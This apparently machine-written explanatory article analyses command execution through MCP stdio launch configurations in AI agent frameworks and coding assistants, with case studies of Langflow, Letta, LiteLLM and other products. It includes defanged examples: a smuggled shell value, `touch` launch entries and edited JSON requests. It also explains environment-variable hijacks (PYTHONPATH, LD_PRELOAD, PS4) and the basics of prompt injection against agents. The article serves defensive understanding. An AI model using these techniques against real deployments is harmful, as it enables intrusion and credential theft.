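# Security of tool-launch mechanisms in AI agent frameworks and coding assistants

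## How AI agents start their tools

An AI agent is a program in which a language model, the kind of system behind ChatGPT or Claude, decides which tools to use, and the software around the model runs them. A tool may read a file, query a database, open a web page or send an email. The model cannot do these things itself, so the agent very often starts another program on the same computer to do them.

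The security of this step depends on who can influence which program starts. A stored entry, usually a few lines of text, names the program. If an outsider can change those lines, or get the agent to change them, the computer runs the outsider's program with the privileges of whoever uses the agent. Security researchers call this "command execution", or "remote command execution" when it happens over a network.

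The problem affects both agent frameworks and coding assistants. Developers use agent frameworks, such as LangChain, to build and run applications where a model chooses and calls tools. Coding assistants, such as Cursor and Claude Code, are agents that read, write and run code on a developer's machine or on a build server, which compiles and tests software automatically.

AI agent frameworks and coding assistants commonly reach their tools through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), an open standard that Anthropic introduced in late 2024. Anthropic has since donated it to the Agentic AI Foundation, a body under the Linux Foundation, as the Model Context Protocol project announced in 2025. Before MCP, the developers of each application had to write separate code for every tool they wanted to connect. With MCP, they write one connection that works with any program that follows the standard. The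 program that offers the tools is the MCP server, and the part of the agent application that starts or contacts it is the MCP client. Under the design in Model Context Protocol's *Architecture* (2026), an application creates a separate client for each server, and a server can be either a local process or a remote service. Even a small script on a laptop that no other machine can reach can be an MCP server.

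### Local and remote servers

Model Context Protocol's *Overview* (2026) defines two standard ways of carrying messages between client and server, which it calls transports: stdio and Streamable HTTP.

Stdio is short for standard input and output. Every program has an input stream and an output stream, which normally connect to the keyboard and the terminal window, but a program that starts another one can connect the new program's streams to itself instead. Model Context Protocol's *stdio* (2026) gives the current rules for communicating this way. The client launches the server as a subprocess, writes requests to its input, one message per line, and reads the replies from its output. To finish, the client closes the input stream, waits, and kills the server if it has not exited. If the server exits unexpectedly, the client should restart it. One configuration entry can therefore cause many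 launches, often with nobody watching. For example, Claude Desktop, Anthropic's desktop application, starts its configured servers every time the user opens it.

With Streamable HTTP, the client sends each message as a web request to a server that someone else has already started, usually on another machine. The operator of a malicious remote server can still send back harmful text or keep data that the agent submits, but the server's code runs on the operator's computer.

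The Model Context Protocol (MCP) originally connected a single application to a server process on the same machine, according to the Agentic AI Foundation. MCP's *Security Best Practices* recommends stdio for local servers because only the client that started the server can talk to it. A local server that listens for web requests may be open to other programs on the machine, or even to a web page in the user's browser. The weak point of stdio is the launch, which happens before the client and server exchange any messages.

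### An ordinary launch configuration

The stored entry that tells the client what to start is the launch configuration. A beginner's guide from the Model Context Protocol project shows how to give Claude Desktop access to the user's files. Cut down to one folder, its entry looks like this:

```json
{
  "mcpServers": {
    "filesystem": {
      "command": "npx",
      "args": [
        "-y",
        "@modelcontextprotocol/server-filesystem",
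        "/Users/maria/Documents"
      ]
    }
  }
}
```

`mcpServers` holds the list of servers, and `filesystem` is only a label for this one. `command` is the program to start, in this case `npx`. It comes with Node.js, the software that runs JavaScript outside a browser. If the package is not already on the machine, `npx` downloads it from npm and then runs it. npm is a registry, a public catalogue where people find and install packages. MCP servers and plugins have registries too. `args` lists the arguments, which are pieces of text passed to `npx` when it starts. The first, `-y`, skips the prompt to confirm the installation, the second is the package name, and the last is the folder that the server may use.

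The entry gives no version number, so the first launch downloads whatever the registry currently supplies under that name. The operating system does not enforce the folder restriction. It is only an instruction to the server's code, so it may not hold if that code is malicious or has bugs. The guide warns that the server runs with the permissions of the user's account and can do anything to files that the user could do by hand.

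Other fields are optional. In VS Code, Microsoft's code editor, `env` sets environment variables, which are named values that a program can read when it starts. They often hold passwords for online services. `envFile` loads more of these variables from a file, and `cwd` sets the working directory, the folder the program starts in. In VS Code's *MCP configuration reference*, the entry for a remote server has a `url` instead of a `command`.

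Fields other than `command` can also be dangerous. When a program asks for `npx` without a full path, the operating system searches for a file of that name. The documentation for *subprocess*, Python's module for launching programs, notes that on Linux and macOS the environment variables supplied for the new process can change where the system searches. Changing those variables can therefore make the same `command` value start a different file.

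### What the operating system does

On Linux, a program usually starts another by making a copy of itself. The copy then calls `execve`, which replaces it with the new program. This call takes a file to run, an array of argument strings and an array of environment variables (*EXECVE(2)*, Linux Programmer's Manual). The operating system passes the strings on without interpreting them, so `npx` in the example receives three separate arguments exactly as the configuration lists them.

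The alternative is to hand a whole line of text to a shell, the command interpreter behind a terminal window. A shell does interpret what it receives. It splits the line at spaces, expands wildcards, and treats characters such as `;` and `|` as instructions. OpenStack's *Use subprocess securely*, guidance from an open-source cloud project, illustrates the danger with a function that pings a network address supplied by the user. Suppose the function pastes the address into a line for the shell, and the user types:

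```
8.8.8.8; touch helloworld.txt
```

The shell pings the address, then runs the `touch` command after the semicolon to create an empty file. If the function had passed a list of arguments instead, `ping` would have received the whole text as one address, and no file would have been created.

Python's documentation recommends lists for this reason, and the official MCP libraries use them. On Windows, however, starting a batch file (`.bat` or `.cmd`) can start a shell even when the calling program supplied a list, according to a Python contributor, zooba, in *[doc] subprocess security considerations needs a Windows-specific exception*.

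Argument lists stop an outsider from inserting a second command into an argument, but they don't protect against an outsider who chooses the program. An entry whose `command` is `touch` and whose only argument is `helloworld.txt` has no special characters and needs no shell, yet the client that starts it still creates the file. The entry could also name a shell as its program, which would again allow everything the list was meant to prevent.

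Once started, a tool acts as the user. On Linux, the new program ordinarily keeps the user and group identity of the program that launched it. On Windows, according to Microsoft's *CreateProcessA function (processthreadsapi.h)*, it runs in the security context of its parent. Desktop operating systems decide whether a process may open a file mainly by checking which account it belongs to, and mostly do not check who wrote the program or why it is running. If Maria can read her SSH keys, the files that let her log in to other computers, then so can a server that her agent started. The server also connects to the network from her machine, so it may reach internal company systems that would refuse outside connections.

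Python's launching module gives the child process all of its parent's environment variables unless the programmer specifies otherwise. Model Context Protocol's *stdio* reference page shows that the official MCP library for Python passes on only a selected set, plus any variables added in the entry's `env` field. This keeps some passwords away from the server but does not protect a password stored in a file.

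### Adoption, and where applications keep their server lists

MCP is now a large target. The Agentic AI Foundation reported that MCP's co-creator David Soria Parra, speaking at a summit in April 2026, put downloads of the protocol's software libraries at more than 110 million a month. The number of users is far smaller, because automated builds download the same library repeatedly. Nordic APIs' *10 Interesting MCP Statistics* counts over 21,000 servers in the public directory MCP.so and over 23,000 in another, Glama, but leaves out companies' private servers. ChatGPT users made 98 times as many MCP tool calls in August 2026 as in January, according to the Agentic AI Foundation's *MCP Usage Surged as the Protocol Went Stateless* (2026).

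None of these figures measures local launches. Much of the ChatGPT traffic probably goes to online services such as Slack and Google Drive, without starting anything on the user's computer. Studies of the applications provide better evidence on launching. Guo and colleagues examined 341 MCP clients in 2025 and found that stdio was still the dominant transport and that few clients had adopted Streamable HTTP. The balance may have shifted since then, given the growth in 2026.

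*An Empirical Study of Model Context Protocol Applications* (Majeed, Mahmoud and Nadi, 2026) is the most useful source on how applications store their launch configurations. The researchers searched GitHub with 46 queries, used a language model to sort and label the results, and checked samples by hand. In a random check of 30 applications, the labels were right 96.5% of the time. Of the 1,723 open-source applications in the collection, 81.1% use an official MCP library to communicate with servers. Among those whose storage could be determined, 85.2% keep the server list in a file, some of them alongside a database, and 14.8% use only a database. The file has no standard name, which makes it harder to scan a company's computers for unexpected entries. The most common name, `mcp.json`, appears in 30.7% of the applications that use a file.

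The collection contains only open-source projects on GitHub, so the percentages may not hold for commercial products. But Claude Desktop, Cursor and VS Code also keep their server lists in files. Any process running under the user's account can normally edit these files, including the agent itself if it has a tool for writing files. VS Code and Cursor also read server lists from inside a project's folder, so a developer who copies someone else's project may also get its server list.

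Majeed and colleagues also found that 37.2% of the applications require the user to approve a tool call before it runs, 77.2% let the user switch servers or tools on and off, and 20.0% have neither control. Approving tool calls does not protect against a bad launch configuration, because the client has already started the server by the time the model can call its tools. Some applications ask separately before starting a server, but Majeed and colleagues did not count how many.

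### What an attack needs

Cantina, a security company, says attacks of this kind require that the application has an interface that starts programs, that untrusted input can reach that interface, and that the process it starts has privileges useful to an attacker.

Any application that supports stdio has the interface, because the transport is meant for starting programs. Maria's filesystem entry meets both this condition and the one about privileges, but it is harmless because she typed it herself and the package is what it claims to be. People disagree about whether the protocol should still restrict what an entry can start or leave that to each application. The security firm OX Security pressed the issue in a disclosure in April 2026.

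The published cases differ most in how untrusted input enters. A stranger may be able to fill in the configuration through a web form. An attacker may also use prompt injection, which means planting instructions in material that an agent reads, such as a web page or a bug report, so that the agent follows them. This works because a model receives its user's instructions and the material it is working on as one stream of text and cannot reliably tell them apart. Somebody may also replace the package that the configuration names, without changing the configuration the user wrote.

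How much the attacker gains depends on the machine. According to Cantina, a process launched on a developer's laptop or a build server may reach resources such as source code, SSH keys, cloud credentials, browser sessions and internal company systems. A sandbox, an enforced limit on the files, network and privileges available to a process, can greatly reduce this access. VS Code offers one for stdio servers on macOS and Linux, but someone has to turn it on in the server's entry.

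When researchers find a product where all three conditions hold, the flaw usually gets a CVE (a public identifier for a specific vulnerability), and the vendor closes the particular path they reported. The known attack paths run through the web interfaces of agent frameworks, deployments that filter commands badly, injected text, files in code repositories, poisoned registries and packages, and remote servers or web pages that trigger a launch on the user's machine.

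## What happens between the configuration and the running process

All of these paths lead to the same few lines of library code. Developers rarely write the launch code themselves. They pass the launch configuration to one of the official software development kits (SDKs) that the Model Context Protocol (MCP) project publishes for the main programming languages, and the SDK starts the process.

The project revised the protocol on 28 July 2026 and announced matching releases of the TypeScript, Python, Go and C# SDKs (Model Context Protocol, 2026). The revision changed how a client and a server make first contact, but not how the client starts the server. The Python code that Model Context Protocol documented in May 2026 finds the program, builds its environment and starts it in the same order as the current code. The Python SDK had reached version 2.3.0 by early October, according to Releasebot's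 *MCP Python SDK Updates & Release Notes* (2026). Version 1 still receives security patches (Model Context Protocol, *Migration Guide*).

### The launch sequence

The Python SDK holds the launch configuration in an object called `StdioServerParameters`. Its main fields are `command`, `args`, `env` and `cwd`, and two more set the text encoding. The object checks types: `command` must be a string and `args` a list of strings. It does not check which program the string names. Simplified, the function that uses the object does this:

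```python
program = find_program(server.command)
environment = default_environment() | (server.env or {})
process = start_process(program, server.args, environment, server.cwd)
# The client can now send its first message.
```

The first line turns the name in `command` into something the operating system can start. On Linux and macOS, the SDK leaves the name unchanged, and the file is looked up when the process starts. On Windows, the SDK itself searches for the file.

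The second line builds the environment from the SDK's selected set of inherited variables and the entry's `env` field. If both define the same variable, the SDK uses the entry's value. FastMCP, a Python library for building MCP servers and clients, lists the inherited variables on Linux and macOS as `HOME`, `LOGNAME`, `PATH`, `SHELL`, `TERM` and `USER`. The SDK skips any inherited value that starts with `()`, because old versions of the Bash shell could run code hidden in such a value. It doesn't check the entry's values for this prefix.

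The third line creates the process. The Model Context Protocol reference page lists two errors that can occur here. One means that the operating system could not start the program, and the other means that the parameters contained a NUL byte, which cannot appear in an argument. The SDK has no error for a program that isn't an MCP server because it cannot detect this at this point.

The SDK opens the message streams between the client and the process only at this point, and the client then attempts the handshake, in which the two sides agree on a protocol version. Under the July specification, the client's first message is a `server/discover` request, which asks the server what it supports. Older servers expect an `initialize` request instead. Model Context Protocol recommends that a client that supports both versions try `server/discover` first and fall back to `initialize` if it gets an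 unrecognised error or no answer. According to Zuplo's *MCP Python SDK 2.0.0*, a compatibility page from a vendor of API software, the two reference SDKs have opposite defaults at version 2.0.0, with Python's starting from the new revision.

The TypeScript SDK works the same way. Model Context Protocol's *client/stdio* documents the same four fields and a `start()` method that launches the process. In the code that Cantina quotes, this method passes `command` and `args` directly to `spawn`, which starts the program. It also passes the merged environment and the working directory. OX Security's *The Mother of All AI Supply Chains* reports the same behaviour in the Java and Go SDKs, although its SDK code examples are all in Python.

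### A command that is not a server

Suppose the parameters object contains this:

```python
StdioServerParameters(command="touch", args=["/tmp/launch-test"])
```

`touch` does not implement MCP, but the SDK accepts both values because they have the right types. It then builds the environment and starts the process. `touch` creates `/tmp/launch-test` and exits, normally within a few milliseconds.

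Meanwhile the client sends its `server/discover` request. `touch` never reads its input, so it does not matter whether the client sends the request before or after `touch` exits. When `touch` exits, its output stream closes without having carried any messages, and the client detects that the connection has ended. The client may then try `initialize`, which also fails, and it reports an error. By then the file is already on the disk. OX Security likewise reports that when the command is not a server, the SDK returns an error after the command has run.

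The process must start before the handshake because only a running server can answer it, so a patch could not reverse this order. Any check on what the program is must therefore happen before the launch and use something other than the program's own replies.

A successful handshake doesn't prove that the launch command only started a server. An attacker can supply a small script that creates a file and then starts a genuine MCP server. The client gets a correct reply and a working list of tools, and the user sees no error.

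If `command` is set to `touch`, the program runs and then the connection fails. The connection also fails if `command` is set to a program that doesn't exist, but in that case the operating system can't start it, so nothing runs. The Python SDK raises a different error in each case, but an application may show both as a failure to connect. Anyone investigating a suspicious entry should find out which error occurred before concluding that the attack failed.

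A program that stays open has more time to act. If it does not reply to `server/discover`, the client waits for a timeout before trying `initialize`, and may then wait again, while the program can keep working. The client shuts the process down when it gives up, but this does not undo what the process has already done.

The command may also run more than once, because the client may treat `touch` as a server that exited unexpectedly and restart it. The Python SDK's launch function contains no restart loop, so whether the command runs again depends on the application built around it. If the application keeps the failed entry in its configuration, it will run the command again the next time it starts its servers.

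### What each field gives an attacker

An attacker often needs to control only one field of an entry, not the whole entry as the `touch` example assumes. For example, a legitimate entry might run `python` with the single argument `server.py`, in a folder where the user keeps that script. The table shows how an attacker who can change only one field could make this entry create an empty file instead.

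| Field | Change to the entry | What the attacker also needs |
|---|---|---|
| `command` | `touch` in place of `python`, which creates an empty file called `server.py` if none exists | Nothing |
| `args` | `-c` and `open('launch-test', 'w')` in place of `server.py` | Nothing |
| `env` | A `PATH` that begins with a folder holding a different program called `python` | A file on the victim's machine |
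| `cwd` | A folder holding a different `server.py` | A file on the victim's machine |

**`command`** gives an attacker the most direct control because it can name any program that the user's account may run. The attacker doesn't have to supply the program, since an ordinary computer already has interpreters, download tools and programs for deleting files.

What an attacker can do by controlling `args` depends on the program that receives them. With `touch`, an attacker can do little more than create files or change their timestamps. Python's `-c` option makes the interpreter run the next argument as code, so an attacker who controls the arguments controls the process. Node.js has a similar option. With `npx`, the attacker can substitute a different package name. An application that fixes `command` but lets users fill in `args` may therefore be little safer, and many lists of permitted commands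 have the same weakness.

**`env`** can change which code a server runs, because many programs read environment variables that control what they load. A reviewer may skip over it because it looks like a place for passwords and settings. Python searches the folders in `PYTHONPATH` for modules before it searches its own standard library, so a file there can replace one that the server expects. On Linux, `LD_PRELOAD` can load an extra library into almost any program as it starts. Both attacks need a file that the attacker has already placed on the machine. An attack through npm's settings doesn't, because npm accepts the address of its registry as an environment variable. An attacker could leave `npx` and its package name unchanged and make it download from a registry they control.

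The SDK's short list of inherited variables does not help with any of this, because the SDK adds the values in `env` without restriction.

**`cwd`** determines which file a relative path such as `server.py` refers to, and it affects programs that look for files in the folder they start in. For example, `npx` can use a package already installed in the current project rather than download one, so a project folder can supply its own version of the package that the entry names. Control of `cwd` alone is useful only to an attacker who can put files on the machine, but a developer who downloads the attacker's project puts them there. According to the Model Context Protocol's TypeScript reference, a server inherits the client's working directory if the field is omitted. For a coding assistant, that directory may be the project the developer has just opened.

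### Why removing shell characters does not help

With the official SDKs, the client launches the process, not the MCP server, and the SDKs do not request a shell. Some press accounts are therefore wrong to describe attackers' commands as reaching a "server-side shell", although the client may be part of a web application running on a company's server. The TypeScript code explicitly sets `shell: false`, and Glama's *cross-spawn.test.ts*, a copy of one of the SDK's automated tests, checks this setting.

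The difference changes the remedy. A developer who believes that the problem is a shell will remove semicolons, pipes and ampersands from the input, but the `touch` entry works without them, as does one that runs a harmful package through `npx`. OX Security's criticism that the SDK performs "no input sanitization" can lead to the same mistake if a reader takes sanitization to mean removing punctuation. In OX's own example of bad practice, the developer passes a user's text directly into `command`. This lets the user choose which program runs, and escaping the text doesn't prevent that.

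The official Model Context Protocol security guidance also uses shell syntax. One of its sample malicious commands runs an `npx` package, then `&&`, then a second command that uploads the user's SSH key. On Linux and macOS, the SDK starts `npx` without a shell, so nothing interprets the `&&`. If an application split that line at the spaces and passed the pieces as arguments, `npx` would start the package and hand it the rest as ordinary text, and the upload command would not run separately. The key would still be at risk, because the package is the attacker's code and can upload the key itself. The guidance lists among the risks that attackers can run any command with the client's privileges.

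### Differences on Windows

The exception for batch files on Windows matters here because it applies to `npx`. On Linux and macOS, `npx` is a script that the operating system can start directly, but on Windows, Node.js supplies it as `npx.cmd`, a batch file that Windows runs through its command interpreter, `cmd.exe`.

On Windows, the Python SDK looks for the command name as written, then tries adding `.cmd`, `.bat`, `.exe` and `.ps1` in turn, according to Model Context Protocol's *utilities*. It passes the file it finds and the arguments to the operating system as a list. If that file is a batch file, `cmd.exe` still interprets the arguments, so characters that would be plain text on Linux can become instructions. Filtering those characters can therefore close a vulnerability when a user controls an argument to `npx`, but it doesn't stop a user who can choose the package or the program.

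The TypeScript SDK uses a helper library, cross-spawn, instead of Node.js's `spawn`. The library's README, in a copy kept by Chromium, lists problems with plain `spawn` on Windows, including a failure to recognise the file extensions that Windows treats as programs. To run a batch file, cross-spawn calls `cmd.exe` itself and escapes the arguments so that the interpreter treats them as text. A command interpreter can therefore still run on Windows even though the SDK passes `shell: false`.

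On Windows, the Python SDK finds the program using the client's own `PATH` before it adds the entry's variables, so an attacker who changes `PATH` in `env` can't use it to substitute a different `python`, as in the table. The changed value still reaches the new process and affects any programs that process starts by name.

The Python SDK can clean up better on Windows, where it places each server in a Job Object. This Windows feature groups a process with the processes it starts, so closing the group kills them all. The SDK assigns the server to the group shortly after Windows creates the process, so anything the server starts in between stays outside the group. The developers acknowledge this gap in a code comment. On Linux and macOS, the SDK deliberately leaves a server's child processes alive if the server exits normally. A command that starts a background program and then exits can therefore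 leave that program running after the client has reported a failed connection.

### How FastMCP and LangChain inherit the behaviour

Many developers use a framework that calls `StdioServerParameters` for them and passes on the same fields. FastMCP's `StdioTransport`, for example, takes `command`, `args`, `env` and `cwd` under the same names. FastMCP warns that a configuration dictionary "can run any command with any arguments", and tells developers whose applications accept server locations from users to validate those locations first.

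FastMCP's client can also start a process from a plain string. It infers from the string what kind of server to use, and if the string names an existing `.py` or `.js` file, it runs that file. An application that asked users for a web address could therefore end up running a local script. FastMCP 4.0 deprecated this behaviour and now prints a warning, but file paths still work. From version 5, the client will treat a string only as a web address.

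LangChain has had two MCP adapters, and both can launch processes. The older one, the `langchain-mcp-adapters` package, takes a dictionary of servers through its `MultiServerMCPClient` class. In the code that Cantina reproduces, the adapter raises an error if a stdio entry lacks `command` or `args`. If both are present, it passes everything to the function that opens the session without checking their values. This matches OX Security's description of LangChain and FastMCP as intermediaries that keep the SDK's logic unchanged.

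`MCPAdapter`, which ships inside LangChain from version 1.4.0 and is still in beta, replaces that package. It is built on FastMCP and addresses the problem with strings by rejecting any that don't look like a web address. LangChain's *Model Context Protocol (MCP)* explains that it does this because server locations from configuration or a model usually arrive as strings. The check is an improvement because it stops a model or user from starting a local script by supplying its path as text.

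The other forms still start processes. If a developer passes a `Path` object, Python's type for file locations, the adapter launches the script it points to. A dictionary with `command` and `args` works as before. The new format is easier to misuse in one respect, because the adapter infers the transport from an entry's other fields. Entries for the old adapter had a `transport` key set to `stdio` or `http`, as LangChain's migration guide shows. The new adapter connects to a remote server if the entry has a `url` and starts a local process if it has a `command`. If an application lets users submit whole entries and expects each to contain a `url`, the application itself has to reject entries that contain a `command`.

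In the standard pattern from LangChain's *Connections*, the launch also happens before the model has read any input or chosen a tool. The program connects to the servers, retrieves their tools and only then creates the agent. If the dictionary lists several servers, the adapter has to contact each one to assemble the list of tools, so a malicious entry starts along with the legitimate ones.

To find code that launches local processes, Cantina advises searching for `StdioServerParameters`, `StdioClientTransport`, `MultiServerMCPClient` and the setting `transport: "stdio"`. A program that has moved to LangChain's new adapter may contain none of these and still start local processes from a dictionary, so the search should also include `MCPAdapter`, FastMCP's `Client` and the key `mcpServers`.

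## Launch commands submitted through framework web interfaces

A web form is the most direct way for an outsider to reach a launch configuration. Many agent frameworks run on a server, and users build agents, connect models and add tools through a web page. To add a stdio tool, the user enters a command, its arguments and sometimes environment variables. When the user submits the form, the framework runs that command on the server.

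Claude Desktop needs the same details, but there the person who enters the command normally owns the computer that runs it. With a web application, these can be different people. A form submitted from a laptop at home can start a process on a company's server, under the account that runs the framework. Anyone who can submit the form can run any program that this account may run, even if the developer built the form as an ordinary settings page.

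Some frameworks also have a button that tests a connection before the user saves it. For a stdio server, the test runs the launch command, even if the user never saves the entry.

### Langflow, from the visitor to the process

Langflow is an open-source tool, owned by IBM, for building agents by connecting components on a canvas. According to its user guide, users can add an MCP server by pasting a JSON entry, filling in a stdio form, or giving the address of a remote server. The stdio form has fields for a name, a command, arguments and environment variables. In Langflow's example, the command is `uvx`, which downloads and runs Python packages, and the first argument is `mcp-server-fetch`.

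This would matter much less if only the server's administrator could submit the form. But OX Security's *MCP Supply Chain Advisory* reports that a stranger could do it without a password. With a harmless command, the attack goes like this:

1. A visitor sends a request to `/api/v1/auto_login`. Langflow returns a session token, a piece of text that marks later requests as coming from a signed-in user.
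2. The visitor uses the token to submit a new stdio server with `touch` as its command and `/tmp/launch-test` as its argument.
3. A Langflow module, `src/lfx/src/lfx/base/mcp/util.py`, reads both values.
4. The module passes them to `StdioServerParameters`.
5. The SDK starts `touch`, which creates the empty file on the server.

The token came from `LANGFLOW_AUTO_LOGIN`, a convenience setting. According to Langflow's *API keys and authentication*, it was on by default in version 1.9 and signed every visitor in to the editor as a superuser, the account with full administrative rights. That suits a program that one person runs on a laptop. Langflow had required credentials for API requests by default since version 1.6, but this did not stop the attack because a session token counted as a credential. IBM's *Unauthenticated Remote Code Execution via Auto-Login Bypass and Code Validation* (2026)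 confirms that the login address issued superuser tokens to any caller on the network.

According to an IBM bulletin on another Langflow flaw, an intruder who can run commands in Langflow's default Docker setup runs them as root, the account with full control inside the container. The intruder can also take the keys for paid model services such as OpenAI's and the credentials for connected databases, and can alter agents that other people have built.

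Langflow's documentation warned users never to expose its ports directly to the internet, but OX Security found more than 915 publicly accessible instances on Shodan, a search engine for internet-connected devices and services. OX does not say how many of them had automatic login switched on, so the number open to the attack may be lower. OX reported the problem to Langflow on 11 January 2026 and tried repeatedly to contact the maintainers, who first acknowledged it directly on 18 March.

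Langflow's fixes were spread over three releases. Version 1.10 added an optional setting that lets only superusers manage MCP servers. Version 1.10.1 corrected incomplete checks on MCP configuration files, a flaw that Intruder lists as CVE-2026-7755. Version 1.11.0 fixed several more flaws, which IBM published on 31 July in *Langflow is affected by security vulnerabilities in Model Context Protocol features*. One of these, CVE-2026-17623, concerns improper validation of the `command` field and is the closest match to OX's report, although IBM's bulletin does not mention OX. Another, CVE-2026-9077, let a logged-in user write arbitrary MCP entries into the configuration files of coding assistants on the same machine, so a request to Langflow could plant a command for a coding assistant to launch later.

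Langflow 1.10.2 fixed a flaw in its filter for dangerous environment variables. Lutra Security's *CVE-2026-12940* (2026) records that the filter's blocklist left out `SHELLOPTS`, `BASHOPTS` and `PS4`, which all change how the Bash shell behaves. In tracing mode, Bash prints the text in `PS4` before each command and runs any command embedded in that text. `SHELLOPTS` can switch tracing on. If Bash runs at any point during the launch, an attacker can therefore use these variables to run a command without changing `command` or `args`. According to the record, the flaw is rated 9.8 out of 10 and an attacker needs no login.

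According to Langflow, its official packages began shipping with automatic login off in version 1.13, which closes OX's route on new installations. Anyone with an active account can still use the stdio form unless an administrator turns on the lock from version 1.10.

If the administrator of an older installation explicitly set `LANGFLOW_AUTO_LOGIN=true`, that setting survives the upgrade. Langflow also warns that turning off automatic login does not cancel sessions or API keys already issued. An intruder who created a key before the upgrade could keep using it afterwards.

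### Who can reach the form

The other products OX examined have much the same web form and pass its contents to the same kind of launch mechanism. They differ mainly in who can submit the form.

In the worst cases, anyone who can open the page can run a command. GPT Researcher, a research agent that writes reports, accepted an MCP configuration without a login. A malicious web page could also reach a copy running on a visitor's machine. Agent Zero, a general-purpose agent framework, runs the commands in a configuration when a user applies it. Fay, a framework for animated digital characters, passes whatever a visitor enters in its web interface to `StdioServerParameters`.

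Langchain-Chatchat, an application for asking questions about a collection of documents, has the same weakness, but the command runs later. Tenable's *CVE-2026-30617* explains that the attacker stores a stdio server through the public management page, and agent activity then triggers the command. An ordinary user could therefore trigger it by starting a conversation long after the attacker has left. Investigators would need to find out who created the entry as well as whose conversation started the process.

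Jaaz, a design assistant, also belongs in this group. OX Security's *Anthropic design choice Exposes 150M+ Downloads and up to 200K Servers* gives Jaaz and Bisheng the same CVE number, CVE-2026-33224, while OX's advisory gives Jaaz CVE-2026-30616. The advisory is right, since both *CVE-2026-30616* (2026) from INCIBE, Spain's national cybersecurity institute, and Lutra Security's *CVE-2026-30616* (2026), a copy of the CVE record, describe the flaw in Jaaz 1.0.30. CVE-2026-33224 is less firmly documented, and Vulners' *CVE-2026-33224* (2026) links it to Bisheng based on press coverage.

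Bisheng, a platform for building company applications on language models, requires a login, but anyone can register, so the login doesn't limit who can submit launch commands. An attacker only has to create an account, open the "Add MCP Server" page and submit a stdio entry. Langflow also allows public registration by default when automatic login is off, but new accounts stay inactive until a superuser approves them.

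LangBot, which connects language models to messaging apps, may have the same problem as Bisheng. OX says an attacker must be logged in. According to OSV's *PYSEC-2026-3473*, the attacker then opens the Extensions page, chooses the MCP tab, adds a stdio server and enters any command. SecureLayer7's *CVE-2026-54449*, a page from a security vendor, adds that LangBot's registration is open and that a self-created account is enough for the attack. If that is correct, the login requirement offers little protection on a public server.

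LiteLLM is a gateway through which a company sends all its requests to different language models and manages the keys and costs in one place. In *Security Update*, LiteLLM's chief executive and chief technology officer, Dholakia and Jaffer (2026), stress that an attacker needed a valid LiteLLM API key. This is a barrier, but companies give such keys to staff and applications so that they can call a model. Before the patch, a key issued for that purpose also let its holder run programs on the gateway, which may hold the company's keys for every model provider it uses.

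| Product | CVE | Access needed | Latest published status |
|---|---|---|---|
| Langflow | CVE-2026-17623 (closest match) | None with automatic login on, otherwise an account | Command check fixed in 1.11.0; automatic login off by default in 1.13 |
| GPT Researcher | CVE-2025-65720 | None | 3.3.7 to 3.4.4 affected; no fix listed |
| Agent Zero | CVE-2026-30624 | None | All versions affected; no fix listed |
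| Fay | CVE-2026-30618 | None | 4.3.1 affected; no fix listed |
| Langchain-Chatchat | CVE-2026-30617 | None | 0.3.1 affected; no fix listed |
| Jaaz | CVE-2026-30616 | None | All self-hosted versions affected; no fix listed |
| Bisheng | CVE-2026-33224 | An account, open to anyone | Patched, but OX names no version |
| LangBot | CVE-2026-54449 | An account, possibly open to anyone | Versions up to 4.10.0 affected; no fix listed |
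| LiteLLM | CVE-2026-30623 and CVE-2026-42271 | An API key | Fixed in 1.83.7-stable |
| Letta | None | An account | Hosted service patched; no fix listed for other copies |
| DocsGPT | CVE-2026-26015 | Unclear | Fixed in 0.16.0 |

"No fix listed" means that OX's advisory listed no fix as of August 2026. Some of these projects may have released one since, so administrators should check the project's release notes. Until a fix is confirmed, it is safest to assume that anyone who can open the page can run commands on the machine.

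OX rates almost every flaw in the table as critical, but other databases sometimes give lower ratings. INCIBE lists the Jaaz flaw at 7.3 out of 10, which counts as high, and Tenable also rates the Langchain-Chatchat flaw as high.

### Options missing from the screen

The last two products in the table are Letta, a platform for agents that remember earlier conversations, and DocsGPT, which answers questions about documents. In both, the page for adding an MCP server offered only remote connection types and no stdio option, so users could not specify a local program through that page.

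OX read Letta's source code and found that the server also accepted stdio. The researchers filled in the page normally, pressed "Test connection" and intercepted the request that their own browser sent. Simplified, the request contained something like this:

```json
{
  "transport_type": "http",
  "url": "https://tools.example.com/mcp"
}
```

They changed the connection type and added a command. A harmless version would be:

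```json
{
  "transport_type": "stdio",
  "command": "touch",
  "args": ["/tmp/launch-test"]
}
```

The server started the program. OX did this on Letta's live service and ran commands on its production servers.

OX calls the technique a "man-in-the-middle" approach. The term usually means intercepting someone else's connection, but here the attacker edits a request from their own browser or writes one from scratch, and no victim's connection is involved. The server cannot tell whether a request came from its web page or from a script, so hiding an option on the page does not stop a person from sending it. Langflow acknowledges this in its release notes about a different feature, an embedded mode that hides parts of the editor. It says the settings "control UI visibility only" and do not block the underlying addresses.

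The check has to happen on the server, which can refuse any request that names stdio or contains a `command` field. Checking for `command` matters most in applications built on LangChain's newer adapter, which infers the transport from an entry's fields.

Both companies patched their hosted services. For self-hosted DocsGPT, the fix is in version 0.16.0, according to the vulnerability record cited in Penligent's *MCP STDIO RCE, The Agent Execution Boundary Failed*. It is unclear whether an attacker needed a DocsGPT account. OX puts DocsGPT in a group labelled "unauthenticated", but that group also includes Letta, and OX reports that the attacker had to log in to Letta.

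### How many servers are exposed

OX's summary reports more than 150 million downloads, more than 7,000 publicly accessible servers and up to 200,000 vulnerable instances. These figures are easy to confuse. Penligent, a security company, warns that the disclosure does not prove that 200,000 internet-facing servers are open to attack today.

The summary does not explain how OX reached any of the three, and refers readers to an eBook for the complete findings. What the figures can support depends on what each one counts:

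- **150 million downloads** measures how widely the affected software has spread. Plenty of applications that use an MCP library never let an outsider choose the command.
- **7,000 servers** is the figure for systems that people can reach over the internet. Reaching a server is only the first step, since it may require a login or have no form for adding tools.
- **200,000 instances** is an upper estimate for the whole ecosystem. An instance inside a company network could count towards it, but an attacker would first need a way into that network.

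OX's smaller numbers are better supported. The count of 915 Langflow instances comes from a named search engine, and OX ran commands on six live platforms, which proves those six were vulnerable at the time.

*Exposed by Design* (Padilla, 2026) measures what a stranger can do with MCP servers that are already running on the internet. Padilla, an independent researcher, ran four scans between 15 and 24 July 2026 and published the results in August. A program called Petrel collected candidate addresses from eleven sources, including package registries, certificate records and search engines such as Shodan, and attempted an MCP handshake with each. The scans confirmed 72, 140, 464 and 296 servers, or 640 different servers across the four runs. A second program, Corvus, sent test requests to 414 of them. The rest rejected the tests, gave malformed replies or had gone offline.

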